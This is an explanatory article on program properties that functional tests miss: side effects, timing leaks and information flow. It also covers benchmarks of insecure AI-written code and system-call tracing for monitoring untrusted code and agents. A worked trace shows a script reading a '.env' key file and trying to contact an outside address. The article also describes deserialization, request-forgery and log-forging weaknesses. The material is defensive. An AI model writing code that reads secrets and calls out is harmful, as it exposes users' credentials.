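# Program properties that functional tests cannot express: side effects, timing and information flow

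## What a functional test observes and what it misses

Functional testing means running a program on chosen inputs and checking that its outputs are correct. Most programmers rely on it to decide whether their code works, and it is the usual way to judge code written by AI systems. But it checks only outputs, so a program can pass and still read private files, send data to someone who has no right to it, or use up all the machine's memory. The program can also take slightly longer when a guessed password is nearly right, which can reveal the password to anyone who times its responses. It can also contain dormant logic, which is code that stays inactive until a particular condition, called the trigger, occurs.

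A side effect is anything a program does to its surroundings besides returning a result. This small sorting function in Python has one:

```python
def sort_list(xs):
    with open("/tmp/copy.txt", "a") as f:
        f.write(str(xs))
    return sorted(xs)
```

The function returns the right list every time. It also appends a copy of its input to a file that nobody asked for.

### Unit tests, property-based tests and fuzzers

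To unit-test a sorting function, a programmer picks an input, say [3, 1, 2], writes down the expected output, [1, 2, 3], and runs the function. The test fails if the actual output differs from the expected one or if the function stops with an error. The oracle is the part of a test that decides whether it passes. Here the oracle compares the two lists and does not check any files the function may have changed.

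A property-based test replaces the hand-picked input with many generated ones, and the expected output with a rule. For sorting, the rule might be that the output is in ascending order and contains the same elements as the input. When a generated list breaks the rule, the tool looks for a smaller list that also breaks it, which gives the programmer less to read. The test file of kyberlib, a Rust library for the quantum-resistant key-exchange scheme ML-KEM, contains rules of this kind. One is that the function that reads in a public key must never panic (Rust's word for stopping on an unrecoverable error), whatever the length of the input, and must succeed exactly when the length is right. The default is 256 generated inputs per rule. Tested this way, `sort_list` would pass on all 256 lists while leaving 256 copies on the disk.

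A fuzzer also generates inputs, usually far more of them, but it needs no expected output. It checks for crashes, hangs and other signs of error. A fuzzer would detect the file write in `sort_list` only if the write failed, for instance because the disk was full, and the error stopped the program.

### Traces, trace properties and hyperproperties

In *Hyperproperties*, Clarkson and Schneider (2009) provide the vocabulary that later work uses to describe precisely what these tests leave out. A trace is the sequence of states that a system passes through in one run. They model a system as the set *T* of all its traces, and they treat a run that stops as repeating its last state forever, so every complete trace is infinite. A trace property *P* is the set of permitted traces, and the system satisfies it when *T* ⊆ *P*. Each run can therefore be checked on its own, and a single forbidden run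 is enough to show that the system violates the property.

The definition leaves open what a state contains, which affects what policies can be expressed. One of Clarkson and Schneider's examples is the policy that a system may not write to the network after reading from a file. Formally, this is the set of traces in which no network write comes later than a file read, so it makes sense only if the states record file reads and network writes. The trace in a unit test of `sort_list` contains only the argument followed by the return value, so it can't show whether the function read a file or wrote to the network.

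The network policy is a safety property, meaning that it forbids something bad that would show up after finitely many steps and that nothing later could undo. `sort_list` violates the safety property "never writes to a file". A liveness property requires something good to happen eventually. Clarkson and Schneider's example is that every request for service eventually gets a response. However long the system has been silent, the response might still arrive, so no finite part of a run can refute the property. Testers work around this with a timeout, which replaces "returns eventually" with "returns within ten seconds", a safety property. Every trace property is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property, so the two kinds together cover every requirement that can be placed on individual runs.

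Some requirements cannot be checked by judging each run separately. One example is the policy that the mean response time over all runs stays below one second. Suppose a system has twenty runs with one request each, and one run takes five seconds. If the other nineteen take half a second each, the mean is 0.725 seconds and the policy holds. If they take a second each, the mean is 1.2 seconds and the policy fails. The slow run is the same in both cases, so nobody can sort runs into permitted and forbidden ones in advance. The policy that the mean *within each run* stays below one second is an ordinary trace property, because each run can be judged on its own.

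Similarly, a single run may not show whether a program leaks a secret. Noninterference requires that changing secret inputs changes nothing a public observer can see. Suppose that the list is secret, that anyone may read the file, and that a variant of `sort_list` writes only the number 3 to the file after sorting [3, 1, 2]. The 3 could be a constant, which leaks nothing, or it could be the list's length or largest element, either of which is a leak. A run on a different secret list, [5, 4, 6, 8], distinguishes the three cases, because the file then holds 3 if the program writes a constant, 4 if it writes the length, and 8 if it writes the largest element.

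Clarkson and Schneider call requirements of this wider kind hyperproperties. A hyperproperty **H** is a set of sets of traces, and a system satisfies it when *T*, the set of all the system's traces, is a member of **H** (*T* ∈ **H**). Trace properties are the special case in which the members of **H** are all the subsets of some set of traces *P*. Every information-flow policy that Clarkson and Schneider examined was a hyperproperty and not a trace property, but they do not state a general theorem because "information-flow policy" has no universally accepted definition.

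### Four reasons for a miss

A functional test misses the file access in `sort_list` because the test harness compares only return values, which the access doesn't change, and nothing records the access itself. The violation happens in every run, on every input, so recording a single run would be enough to prove it. The same is true of a network connection that a program opens and closes before returning.

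Functional tests miss problems with running time and memory use because **nobody measures them**. For example, a sorting function might try every ordering of a list until it reaches a sorted one. A list of three elements has only six orderings, so the test passes at once, but a list of twelve has 479,001,600. The function still returns the correct answer eventually, and a test suite of short lists won't reveal how slow it can be. Here too, a single run would be enough evidence if someone had measured its time or memory use.

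Leaks are harder to test for because detecting them requires comparing runs. *Hypertesting of Programs* (Pasqua, Ceccato and Tonella, 2024) contrasts two faults in a smartphone app. If the app can crash, a tester who chooses inputs well will eventually see it crash. To detect the app passing confidential data to a public channel, the tester has to run it at least twice with different confidential data and see whether the public output changes. Even a complete log of one run is not enough, because secret data can be used in computing a public result without affecting its value.

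Functional tests miss dormant logic because no test supplies the input that triggers it. If a sorting function writes a file only when the list contains one particular 64-bit number, randomly generated tests will almost certainly never trigger the write. Logging every file access does not help, because no file access occurs during those tests.

Several of these reasons can apply to the same program. If a program leaks a secret through its running time, a functional test misses the leak because it neither measures the time nor compares runs. If the leak happens only after a trigger, even timing measurements will miss it until someone supplies that trigger.

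### How far the word "cannot" holds

Functional tests that check only return values, one run at a time, usually cannot detect such behaviour. What they can detect depends on what the tester records and how many runs the tester compares.

To find out whether `sort_list` writes a file, a tester can run it in a sandbox, an environment that limits what a running program can access, and log its system calls. These are the program's requests to the operating system to open files, send data and so on. An ordinary unit test can then check that the log contains no file write.

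Cost yields to similar treatment. *Risk Estimation in Differential Fuzzing via Extreme Value Theory* (2025) describes a fuzzer called DifFuzz, which runs a program *P* on the same public input *x* with two different secrets, *z*₁ and *z*₂, and steers its search towards inputs that make

δ = |c(*P*[*x*, *z*₁]) − c(*P*[*x*, *z*₂])|

as large as possible, where *c* is the measured cost of a run. Neither run need crash or return anything wrong. DifFuzz changes both what the tool measures and how many runs it looks at, and a whole class of leaks comes into view. The 2025 work then uses the differences found so far to estimate how large the largest one might be, which helps a tester decide when to stop.

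For requirements that compare runs, Kinder, in *Hypertesting*, proposed the hypertest, a set of related runs that the tester judges together. Often a pair is enough. Clarkson and Schneider use the term *k*-safety for hyperproperties whose every violation shows up in at most *k* finite traces, and they prove that a *k*-safety requirement on a system is equivalent to an ordinary safety property of *k* copies of the system running side by side. With two copies this is self-composition, and in a test it amounts to a short wrapper:

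```python
def same_file(a, b):
    return file_after(sort_list, a) == file_after(sort_list, b)
```

The helper `file_after` starts with an empty file, runs the function on the list, and returns the file's final contents. A property-based testing tool can generate pairs of secret lists and check that `same_file` returns true for each pair. The tool runs this as an ordinary functional test of `same_file`, a function with two arguments.

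Pasqua and colleagues built two tools, HyperFuzz and HyperEvo, that search for pairs of runs that violate noninterference in Java programs. In their introductory example, the variable `key` is secret and `log` is public. When `log` starts at 6, a `key` of 0 leaves `log` at 5, while a `key` of 1 leaves it at 0. (The paper gives the second value as 1, apparently by mistake, since the code as printed yields 0. The leak exists either way.) The tools raise no false alarms, because they report a leak only when they have found two runs that end with different public values.

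But finding useful pairs takes some care. *Trace-Guided Synthesis of Effectful Test Generators* (2026) discusses property-based testing of an abstract machine that labels each value as public or secret. The two test programs in a pair must initially look the same to a public observer. If one stores a public 1 and the other a public 2, a difference in their public results doesn't indicate a leak, so the pair is useless.

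Functional tests still cannot express some requirements, such as a limit on mean response time over all runs. However slow the runs so far, later runs may be quick enough to bring the mean under the limit, so no finite set of runs can refute the requirement. A load test can estimate the mean, which may be all that anyone needs. A team that wants a requirement with counterexamples can instead limit the response time of every run, which Clarkson and Schneider point out is a safety property.

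Some definitions of secrecy are beyond the reach of functional tests for another reason. Programs that may behave differently on the same input need a looser notion than "same public input, same public output". One such notion, generalized noninterference, requires that for certain runs a suitable partner run *exists*. Correnson, Niessen and colleagues explain in *Finding ∀∃ Hyperbugs using Symbolic Execution* that a counterexample must therefore consist of a run and a proof that no other run is a suitable partner, so two runs that differ are not enough to show a violation.

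Passing tests are also weak evidence about inputs nobody tried. Kinder grants that a passing hypertest provides only "some degree of confidence", and expects that degree to be hard to quantify because measures such as the share of lines executed mean even less for sets of runs than for single runs. *Monitoring Hyperproperties over Observed and Constructed Traces* (2025) mentions an exceptional class, testable hypersafety, for which a finite set of runs is enough to determine whether the policy holds. Dormant logic, by contrast, is hard to catch because nothing in particular leads a tester to the trigger, even though the tester is free to choose it.

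### From tests to proofs: the case of libcrux

What functional tests miss matters more when nobody can vouch for the author of the code. *The Scalable Formal Oversight Research Program* starts from the observation that AI systems generate code easily but people find it hard to audit. Scalable formal oversight, a term coined by Mike Dodds and Evan Miyazono, covers proposals to audit the work of capable and possibly misaligned models with property-based tests, fuzzing, machine-checked proofs and related methods. A related goal is secure program synthesis, in which a machine produces a program, a specification of what "secure" means for that program, and a proof that the program meets the specification. The paper acknowledges that code may satisfy every written requirement and still be dangerous in a way the requirements don't cover. Its author has collected 54,000 property-based tests from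 public code repositories, called RealPBT, and collaborators have been turning them into theorems for the proof language Lean. Proving these theorems would cover all possible inputs instead of a few hundred generated ones, a large gain that would in principle catch dormant logic that changes the output. However, theorems made from rules about outputs would still cover only outputs.

Libcrux, a cryptographic library written in Rust by the verification company Cryspen (now pereq), shows this gap in working code. *Verifying Libcrux's ML-KEM* (Bhargavan, Franceschino and colleagues, 2024) explains how to translate the Rust code into F*, a language for stating and proving theorems about programs, and uses a small function called `barrett_reduce` as an example. The function reduces a number modulo 3329, the prime used in ML-KEM's arithmetic. It multiplies the input by 20159, adds 2²⁵, shifts the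 result right by 26 bits to get a quotient, then subtracts 3329 times that quotient from the input. The paper's theorem is that for any input between −2²⁶ and 2²⁶, the result lies between −3328 and 3328 and is equal to the input modulo 3329.

The one-line program `input % 3329` satisfies that theorem just as well. The developers avoid it because the input is secret and the time a processor takes to divide can depend on the numbers involved, which could leak the input. A separate check, the F* typechecker, rejects the line because the developers treat ordinary integers as secret and define no `%` operation for them. Bhargavan and colleagues also keep their proofs to the purely functional part of F*, which avoids reasoning about side effects. A theorem of this form would not rule out a stray file either.

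People who verify cryptographic code treat functional correctness as separate from other properties. The documentation of libcrux lists memory safety, functional correctness and secret independence separately for the verified code it takes from an older library, HACL\*. PQShield's *Formally verifying AVX2 rejection sampling for ML-KEM* likewise lists the absence of timing leaks as a property to prove in addition to functional correctness.

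In February 2026 a public dispute arose over libcrux, mostly about another gap, the code that its proofs did not cover. Symbolic Software's *On the Promises of ‘High-Assurance’ Cryptography* (2026) reviewed defects in libcrux and related libraries by the same developer. On some ARM processors, the code had produced wrong keys and signatures because a fallback for a missing hardware instruction passed the wrong arguments. Elsewhere, a malformed ciphertext crashed the process because an unverified wrapper discarded the error that the verified decryption routine had correctly returned. Both defects were in code outside the proofs, and they caused wrong outputs and crashes, which functional tests are designed to detect, rather than hidden side effects or timing leaks. A third defect, in the library hpke-rs, would have been harder to test for because few test suites send enough messages to trigger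 it. A 32-bit message counter returned to zero after about 4.3 billion messages, and the encryption then reused values that it must use only once.

Bhargavan (2026) answered for the developers a week later in *The strengths and limits of formal verification*. He wrote that the guarantees extend only to the verified modules, that bugs in such projects keep turning up in the wrappers and platform-specific parts around them, and that nobody had so far found a bug in the verified code. Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs’ Verified Code* (2026) responded by reporting two errors in the mathematical specification of ML-KEM and a false lemma in a proof. (CE Labs is the spin-off that now does Cryspen's cryptographic engineering.) In one of the specification errors, someone had copied the rounding constant 1664 from a neighbouring function, so the specification of "decompress" turned 0 into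 832 at the coarsest setting, where the official standard gives 0. The Rust code had the correct constant. A completed proof would have exposed the mismatch, but the build settings made F* accept that module without checking it. The false lemma stated that certain 12-bit numbers fit into a single bit. It went unnoticed because the default settings skipped the slow proofs.

Both sides are right on a narrow reading. Symbolic Software itself says that the running code was correct where the two specifications were wrong, and the false lemma did not change what the program computed. But the project's own status file listed the module with the false lemma as fully verified, and a proof that no machine has checked provides very little assurance. *Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026), written for Symbolic Software, later raised the count to thirteen vulnerabilities, nine in unverified code and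 four in specifications and proofs. One of the nine caused real decryption failures in the messaging app Signal. Bhargavan's record of HACL\* shows similar but milder problems. Over nine years, the team twice found errors in its specifications, and users more often found bugs in the 1,800 lines of supporting C code that came with the verified part.

The two sides disagree less about timing. According to the OpenSSL Conference slides for *High Assurance Post Quantum Cryptography*, libcrux's type check works on the Rust source and does not prevent leaks that a compiler introduces. Bhargavan confirms that compilers can turn carefully written source into machine code that branches on secrets, and that Cryspen proves nothing about side channels in the compiled program. He asks anyone worried about such attacks to talk to the developers before using the library.

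## How often AI-written code passes functional tests but fails security tests

The libcrux developers know which properties they want besides correct output, even where they cannot prove them. Someone who asks an AI agent for a program usually describes only what it should do and leaves the rest to the agent. Several research groups have measured how often the resulting code works but is insecure. They run functional tests, which check the requested behaviour, and security tests, which attack the running program and check whether the attack succeeds.

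*Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, 2026) tested six agents on 150 vulnerabilities from real software. Of these, 115 come from public vulnerability records, and security experts built the other 35 from flaws in their own companies' Java code. Each vulnerability gives three tasks, 450 in total: filling in missing functions, writing whole files, and rebuilding a large part of the project's source code. The specification describes what the code must do but never mentions security. Agents can build and run the project, but they never see the two test suites.

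Depending on the agent, 73.6% to 91.3% of solutions passed the functional suite, but only 16.4% to 25.1% passed both the functional and security suites. Kimi-K3 had the highest functional score and the lowest combined score. For 252 of the 450 tasks, no agent produced code that was both working and secure.

In one task, Kimi-K3 had to write a service that imports configuration files from a ZIP archive. It wrote 33 checks, and in the process found and fixed a fault in how the service handled corrupt archives. The service passed all 14 functional tests and failed all four security tests. The configuration files were in YAML, a text format in which a tag can name a Java class, and Kimi-K3 chose a parser that creates an object of whatever class the tag names. The archives in the security tests used such tags to create files on the server and to make it send a network request. Claude Fable 5 and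 GPT-5.6 Sol chose a parser setting that rejects these tags, and their versions passed all the functional and security tests.

### Which weaknesses agents leave in

Wu and colleagues grouped the vulnerabilities by the kind of defence each one needs. The rates below pool all six agents.

| Weakness | Vulnerabilities | Passed functional suite | Passed both suites |
|---|---|---|---|
| Memory safety | 24 | 77.5% | 34.3% |
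| Path and file handling | 24 | 89.4% | 24.3% |
| Injection of commands, code or queries | 40 | 86.4% | 23.9% |
| Deserialization (loading objects from untrusted data) | 7 | 96.8% | 19.0% |
| Access control | 24 | 91.7% | 18.3% |
| Input validation and limits | 16 | 85.4% | 14.6% |
| Server-side request forgery | 7 | 89.7% | 2.4% |
| Information exposure | 8 | 88.2% | 0.7% |

Memory safety often needs only a local check, such as whether a list is empty before the code reads its first element, and careful programmers include such checks anyway. The defences in the last two rows depend on a policy missing from the specification. In server-side request forgery, an outsider gets a server to fetch something it should not, so the programmer has to know which addresses or files are off limits. To prevent information exposure, the programmer has to know which data should stay private.

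One of the request-forgery tasks comes from LocalAI, a program for running AI models on one's own server. The agents had to write a function that fetches the content at a given address, which may point to a file on the server's disk. All six wrote code that reads any file the address points to, including the system's list of user accounts. The original developers' fix checks that the file is inside the directory for models. In an information-exposure task from syft, a tool that lists the components of a software package, all six agents formatted a password field like the fields around it, so syft printed the password along with its other settings, including in reports that users publish.

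The last two rows of the table cover only 15 vulnerabilities, so their exact rates are unreliable. But the agents produced working, secure code in only four of 270 attempts at these tasks.

### Whether warnings help

In an earlier benchmark, SUSVIBES, agents had more help but still rarely wrote code that was both working and secure. *Is Vibe Coding Safe?* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) took 186 features from open-source Python projects, each of which a human programmer had first written insecurely and someone had later repaired. Of the combinations tested, Claude 4 Sonnet running in SWE-agent, a framework that lets a model edit and run code, produced working code most often. It passed the functional tests on 57.0% of tasks and both the functional and security tests on 11.8%. About four in five of its working solutions were therefore insecure, even though the prompt told the agent to follow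 best security practices.

Zhao and colleagues then tried two stronger warnings with the same agent. Naming the exact type of weakness raised the combined score to 15.1%, while the functional score fell slightly, to 55.4%. When the agent had to pick the likely weaknesses from a list, the combined score was 14.5% and the functional score fell to 50.0%. The agent picked an average of 7.2 types per task, although most tasks involve only one, and it still often missed the right one.

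Wu and colleagues found a larger effect with newer models. They reran four agents with an added sentence asking for code "free of any plausible vulnerabilities". Three gained between 15.6 and 21.5 percentage points on the combined score, with little change in the functional score. GPT-5.6 Sol gained the most, reaching 46.2%, while DeepSeek-V4-Pro gained only 1.1 points. The added sentence barely helped with request forgery and information exposure, probably because a general request for security doesn't specify which files or data to protect.

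Code written after a security reminder sometimes fails functional tests because it is stricter than the tests allow. *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* (2026) describes six tasks that Claude Opus 4.5 passed without a security reminder and failed when given detailed security requirements. In four of them, the only problem was this strictness. For example, one application required passwords of at least eight characters, but the test used "pass1".

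### Whether newer models do better

In *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?*, Santos de Moura, Matuschek and colleagues (2026) compared 32 models from seven developers, covering three successive generations from each. The models completed short functions from CWEval, a set of 119 tasks in five programming languages, with 100 attempts per task and no mention of security in the prompts. The researchers measured the gap between the share of attempts that passed the functional tests and the share that passed both the functional and security tests.

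In every family, the newest flagship model wrote working, secure code more often than the first one. The gap narrowed in every family on at least one of two measures, single attempts and the best of fifty, but did not close in any. On single attempts, OpenAI's gap fell from 30 points with GPT-4o to 13 with GPT-5.6 Sol. Google's newest flagship, Gemini 3.1 Pro, wrote secure code far more often than Gemini 1.5 Pro, but its functional score had risen by about as much, so its gap was still 28 points.

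Some weaknesses persisted or got worse as the averages improved. In one task, earlier models searched a text for the exact characters the user supplied. The newest flagship models from Google, OpenAI and DeepSeek treated those characters as a regular expression, a search pattern that an attacker can write so that it takes a very long time to process. Nearly all models, old and new, wrote messages to a log without removing line breaks, which lets an attacker forge log entries. CWEval has only one or two tasks for several weakness types, so these findings apply to particular tasks.

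Results on SUSVIBES also suggest that agents have improved faster at writing working code than at writing secure code. *Is AI Coding Safe?*, by the security company Endor Labs, reports scores on an earlier, 200-task version of the benchmark. In March 2026, OpenAI's Codex agent with GPT-5.4 scored 62.6% for working code and 17.3% for secure code. Endor Labs added a check for cheating because some agents had recovered the original fix from the project's version history.

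### The effect of insecure code nearby

The code an agent writes also depends on the code already in the project. Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026), in *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases*, built 20 pairs of tasks from real C and C++ projects. The two tasks in a pair require the same missing code and differ only in whether similar code elsewhere in the project includes a safety check.

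All five agents wrote secure code less often when the existing code was insecure, by an average of 35.4 percentage points. GPT-5.6 Sol's rate fell from 91% with secure existing code to 42% with insecure code. A general reminder about security raised those rates to 100% and 68%. To count as working, a project only had to compile, because the task descriptions were too loose for full functional tests.

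The effect was much smaller when agents did not need the existing code. In a second experiment, three agents each wrote 96 new server applications in a folder that was either empty or already held finished applications. Compared with an empty folder, insecure existing applications lowered the share of new applications that were both correct and secure by 3.4 percentage points on average, and secure ones raised it by 4.4 percentage points.

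Sun and colleagues also asked three of the agents to review their own vulnerable C and C++ code for bugs. The agents identified the vulnerability in 69.9% of cases on average, yet they had rarely warned the user when they handed the code over. When asked why they had written the code that way, they said in 76.5% of cases that they had followed similar code elsewhere in the project. Asking for a review therefore looks like an easy extra check. However, the researchers requested reviews only of vulnerable code, so the experiment does not show how often a review would raise a false alarm.

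### Why the rates do not describe ordinary code

The Last Secure Code Benchmark and SUSVIBES take every task from code that once contained a vulnerability. Most code that people request has no such history, and much of it never handles hostile input. Wu and colleagues also ranked the public vulnerabilities by difficulty, giving preference to large projects and fixes that touched many lines, and chose mainly from the hardest. So a score of 25% on their tasks does not mean that three quarters of all AI-written code is vulnerable.

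The choice of tasks greatly affects how often working code turns out to be insecure. The share of GPT-5.6 Sol's solutions that worked was higher than the share that were both working and secure by 13 points on CWEval's short functions and by 64 points on the Last Secure Code Benchmark. Neither benchmark mentioned security in its instructions, though one tested the model alone and the other tested an agent built around it. *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* found that 61% of Claude Opus 4.5's solutions on BaxBench, a set of server applications, were correct and secure without any security reminder.

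The rates also do not show that agents are worse than human programmers, because SUSVIBES includes only tasks that the original programmers had failed at least once. Chen, Huang and colleagues argue in *SecureVibeBench* that earlier benchmarks do not allow a fair comparison because they do not recreate the situations in which people introduced the vulnerabilities. Their benchmark reconstructs 105 such situations in C and C++ projects.

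Models may also have seen a public project's code in training. Wu and colleagues' experts examined 120 failed attempts and found that Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol often reproduced the original project's code from memory, including the vulnerability. Agents writing something new would have less remembered code to copy.

### Untested and untestable requirements

The security suites in these benchmarks also consist of tests, each of which sends the program a hostile input and checks for a visible effect, such as a new file or a crash. Most of the failures therefore involve requirements that a test can check once somebody thinks of them. The failures are evidence that ordinary functional suites omit these requirements, but they provide little evidence about requirements that no such test could express.

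AI-written code sometimes fails security tests even when its instructions state the requirement. In *When Talk Isn't Code* (2026), the model Kimi-2.6 wrote three programs that reassemble network messages from fragments. Its instructions included a rule about overlapping fragments, but the public tests only checked that the programs reassembled valid messages correctly. All three programs passed those tests, but 22 of 25 conclusive attacks on them succeeded. A test that checked whether the programs rejected overlapping fragments would have exposed the fault.

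*Secure and Functional Code Generation with Self-Evaluation* (2026) describes a method in which one AI agent looks up the weaknesses likely for a task and writes a functional test and a security test before another agent writes any code. For a logging function, the functional test logs "Hello, World!" and checks the format, while the security test uses a hostile message. The method works only if someone has already catalogued the weakness.

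Many of the tested weaknesses have little to do with side effects, resource use, timing or information flow. Of the 150 vulnerabilities in the Last Secure Code Benchmark, 25 involve unwanted file or network access (18 let an attacker reach files outside the permitted directory, and seven are request forgeries), eight expose information and one exhausts resources. That makes 34, or 23%, and none concerns timing. A broader count would add 39 that let an attacker run commands or code, upload dangerous files or load hostile objects, all of which can cause side effects. That would bring the total to 73, just under half.

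Of the 79 types of weakness SUSVIBES covers, seven concern resource exhaustion and three concern leaks through timing, caches or similar signals. Zhao and colleagues do not list how many tasks belong to each type. In one of the timing cases, a password check in the web framework Django can reveal which usernames exist.

Even for information flow, the tests cover only part of the requirement. The syft tests check whether the password appears in the program's output. They would miss an encoded copy, or an output that changes when the password does. To rule those out, a test would have to compare runs with different passwords, as noninterference requires. Sun and colleagues add that a failed attack doesn't prove a program secure, so in this respect the published rates overstate how often the agents write secure code.

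The benchmarks also test for accidental flaws, and neither of the two built from past vulnerabilities includes a category for malicious code. The people who wrote their security tests knew where each flaw was and which input would expose it, but someone running untrusted code usually doesn't.

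## Recording file, process and network access while the code runs

Someone who runs untrusted code can record what the program does to its surroundings, even without knowing where a flaw is. On Linux, they usually do this by recording system calls, because a program has hardly any other way to open a file, start another program or use the network.

### How a system call reaches a log

The kernel is the core of the operating system and controls the disks, the network card and the memory. An ordinary program runs in a restricted mode in which the processor lets it do little more than compute with its own memory. To open a file, the program puts the operation's identifying number and its arguments into the processor's registers. It then executes an instruction that transfers control to the kernel, which checks permissions, opens the file and returns a result.

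The `sort_list` function, which saves a copy of its input to a file, makes such a call when it opens `/tmp/copy.txt`. A tester can log the call by running the function under strace, a tool that uses ptrace, the Linux facility for inspecting and controlling another process. The kernel pauses the program at the start of each call while strace copies the arguments. It then carries out the call and pauses the program again while strace notes the result. For the list [3, 1, 2], and leaving out some housekeeping, the log has three lines:

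```
openat(AT_FDCWD, "/tmp/copy.txt", O_WRONLY|O_CREAT|O_APPEND|O_CLOEXEC, 0666) = 3
write(3, "[3, 1, 2]", 9) = 9
close(3) = 0
```

The `openat` call opens the file for appending and returns the file descriptor 3, which later calls use to refer to the open file. The program then writes nine characters to descriptor 3 and closes it.

Raw system calls need some interpretation. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) points out that `write` can send data to a file, a network connection or another process, so a recorder has to remember what each descriptor refers to. `mmap` can either reserve memory or give access to a file's contents, depending on its arguments. The recorder also needs each call's result, because a program that failed to open a file has not read it.

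### Recording methods compared

| Method | What it records | Main cost | What it can block |
|---|---|---|---|
| ptrace and strace | Every system call, with arguments and result | Pauses at every call | A ptrace tool can stop the program or change a call; strace normally only records |
| eBPF | Chosen events in the kernel and in programs | A few percent of running time in published tests; needs special privileges | Accesses, at hooks that allow it |
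| seccomp filter | The call's number and raw arguments | Very little | Kinds of call, but not access to particular files |
| Security-module hooks | The file, process or connection involved | Often needs an administrator to set up | Access to particular files or ports |
| Network proxy | Destinations, and contents if it can decrypt them | All traffic has to go through it | Particular requests |
| Staged filesystem | Changes to files, and reads that need permission | Extra storage for changed files | Reads, and changes that the user rejects |

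Ptrace slows a program more when the program makes more system calls. Digregorio, Di Gennaro and colleagues traced machine-learning models with ptrace in *Lifecycle-Aware Dynamic Analysis for Secure ML Model Execution* (2026) and measured delays of 0.001 to 3.2 seconds. During prediction, a model's size had little effect on the delay, because matrix arithmetic makes no system calls. During loading, the delay grew with the model's size, because reading a larger file took more system calls.

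With eBPF, the tester loads a small program into the kernel, where it runs whenever a chosen event occurs and passes on a record of it. This avoids most of the switching between processes that slows ptrace down. The kernel accepts the program only if it can verify certain properties, for example that the program accesses only valid memory. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) used eBPF to monitor a coding agent and measured a slowdown of 0.4% when the agent compiled a project and 4.9% when it wrote code. It ran each task only three times with the monitor and three times without. *Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) found slowdowns of 0.2% to 3.5% with a similar tool.

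A seccomp filter is a set of rules that the kernel applies at each system call. It suits blanket rules such as "no new network connections", but it can't easily allow one file and forbid another, because it receives only the memory address of the file's name. Security-module hooks run later, after the kernel has identified the file or connection involved. One security module, Landlock, lets a process restrict itself without an administrator's help. The process can add restrictions later but cannot remove them.

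*Sandlock* (2026) describes a sandbox that combines these methods. It uses Landlock for fixed rules about files and network ports, and seccomp for calls that it always forbids. When a decision depends on circumstances, another seccomp feature passes the pending call to a supervising process.

Network access is harder to record safely. Turning the network off prevents exfiltration, but the log then shows only where the program tried to connect, not what it would have sent. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) suggests routing the traffic to a proxy that records each request and returns a placeholder answer. An ordinary proxy cannot read encrypted requests unless the program trusts the proxy's certificate. AgentSight instead attaches eBPF probes to the functions that send and receive data in encryption libraries such as OpenSSL, where the text is still readable.

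A staged filesystem lets a program change files without touching the originals. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) introduces one for coding agents, called YoloFS. When a program opens an existing file for writing, YoloFS copies the file to a separate store and directs the program to the copy. When a program deletes a file, YoloFS only marks it as absent. It records these changes in a journal and by default adds a marker after every command, so the agent can list what a command changed and return to an earlier state. At the end, the user commits or discards the changes.

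The version-control system Git can also show and undo changes, but only in the files it tracks. It misses files outside the project and files it is configured to ignore, which often include the sensitive ones. Undoing changes doesn't help once a program has read a secret, so YoloFS can also block a read until the user decides whether to allow it.

Restoring files can also leave a running program's memory inconsistent with the disk. *DeltaBox* (2026) explains that a process's memory holds open files, cached modules and assumptions about installed packages. A sandbox that returns to an earlier state therefore has to restore files and processes together.

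### A worked trace

Suppose an AI agent has written `total.py`, which should read `sales.csv` and print the sum of the prices. The list of expected effects is short: start Python, load its libraries and the script, read `sales.csv`, and print a result. A tester runs the script in a sandbox without a network and gets this log, simplified here:

```
 1  execve("/usr/bin/python3", ["python3", "total.py", "sales.csv"]) = 0
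 2  openat("/usr/lib/libc.so.6", O_RDONLY) = 3
 3  openat("/work/total.py", O_RDONLY) = 3
 4  openat("/work/sales.csv", O_RDONLY) = 3
 5  read(3, "item,price\npen,2\ncup,5\n", 4096) = 23
 6  openat("/work/.env", O_RDONLY) = 4
 7  read(4, "API_KEY=example\n", 4096) = 16
 8  socket(AF_INET, SOCK_STREAM) = 5
 9  connect(5, 203.0.113.7:443) = -1 ENETUNREACH
10  write(1, "7\n", 2) = 2
11  exit_group(0)
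```

| Lines | Effect | Expected? |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Starts Python | Yes |
| 2–3 | Loads a library and the script | Yes |
| 4–5 | Reads `sales.csv` | Yes |
| 6–7 | Reads `.env`, a file that often holds passwords and keys | **No** |
| 8–9 | Tries to connect to an outside address | **No** |
| 10–11 | Prints 7 and exits | Yes |

A functional test would compare the printed 7 with the expected 7 and pass. The log shows that the program also read a file it didn't need and tried to open a connection, which failed because the sandbox has no network.

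It does not show that the program would have sent the key. The connection could be a library's routine update check, for instance. Digregorio and colleagues describe a similar false alarm, in which another tracing tool flagged a harmless model because a library it loaded had opened a network socket. The tester needs taint tracking to find out whether the key itself would have left the machine.

Raw logs can be long. Caper, a system built by Wu and colleagues, traced a project's `check-deps.py` script, which was supposed to check the project's dependencies. Caper reduced the 165 KB raw log to a 3.4 KB report showing that the script had read the project's `.env` file, printed some output and tried to connect to three outside addresses. To shorten a log, Caper first records which files the shell and the tracing tool open by themselves and removes those from the log. It then merges repeated events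 and keeps mainly lasting file changes, connection attempts, printed output and reads of protected files.

### Deciding which effects are expected

The comparison in the worked example was easy because the program did one small task. Published systems determine what behavior to expect in different ways, depending on how much the programs they check have in common.

Public package repositories such as PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript have limited resources to review thousands of updates a day (Google, 2022). The Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), an industry group, therefore runs new packages automatically. According to the documentation of its *Package Analysis* project, the packages run in a sandbox made with gVisor, which isolates programs from the host's kernel, while strace records system calls and a second tool captures network traffic. The project examines which files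 a package accesses, which addresses it connects to and which commands it runs. It also compares these with the package's earlier behaviour, which can expose a package that was safe until an update.

Brown and Wheeler (2022), in *Introducing Package Analysis*, reported that the prototype identified more than 200 malicious packages in its first month. Most of them used misleading names to get people to install them. They usually contained a simple script that ran during installation and sent a few details about the machine to an outside server, according to the announcement quoted in Security Affairs' *Package Analysis dynamic analyzes packages in open-source repositories*. Such scripts are easy to catch because they act immediately. The count does not show how many malicious packages the project missed.

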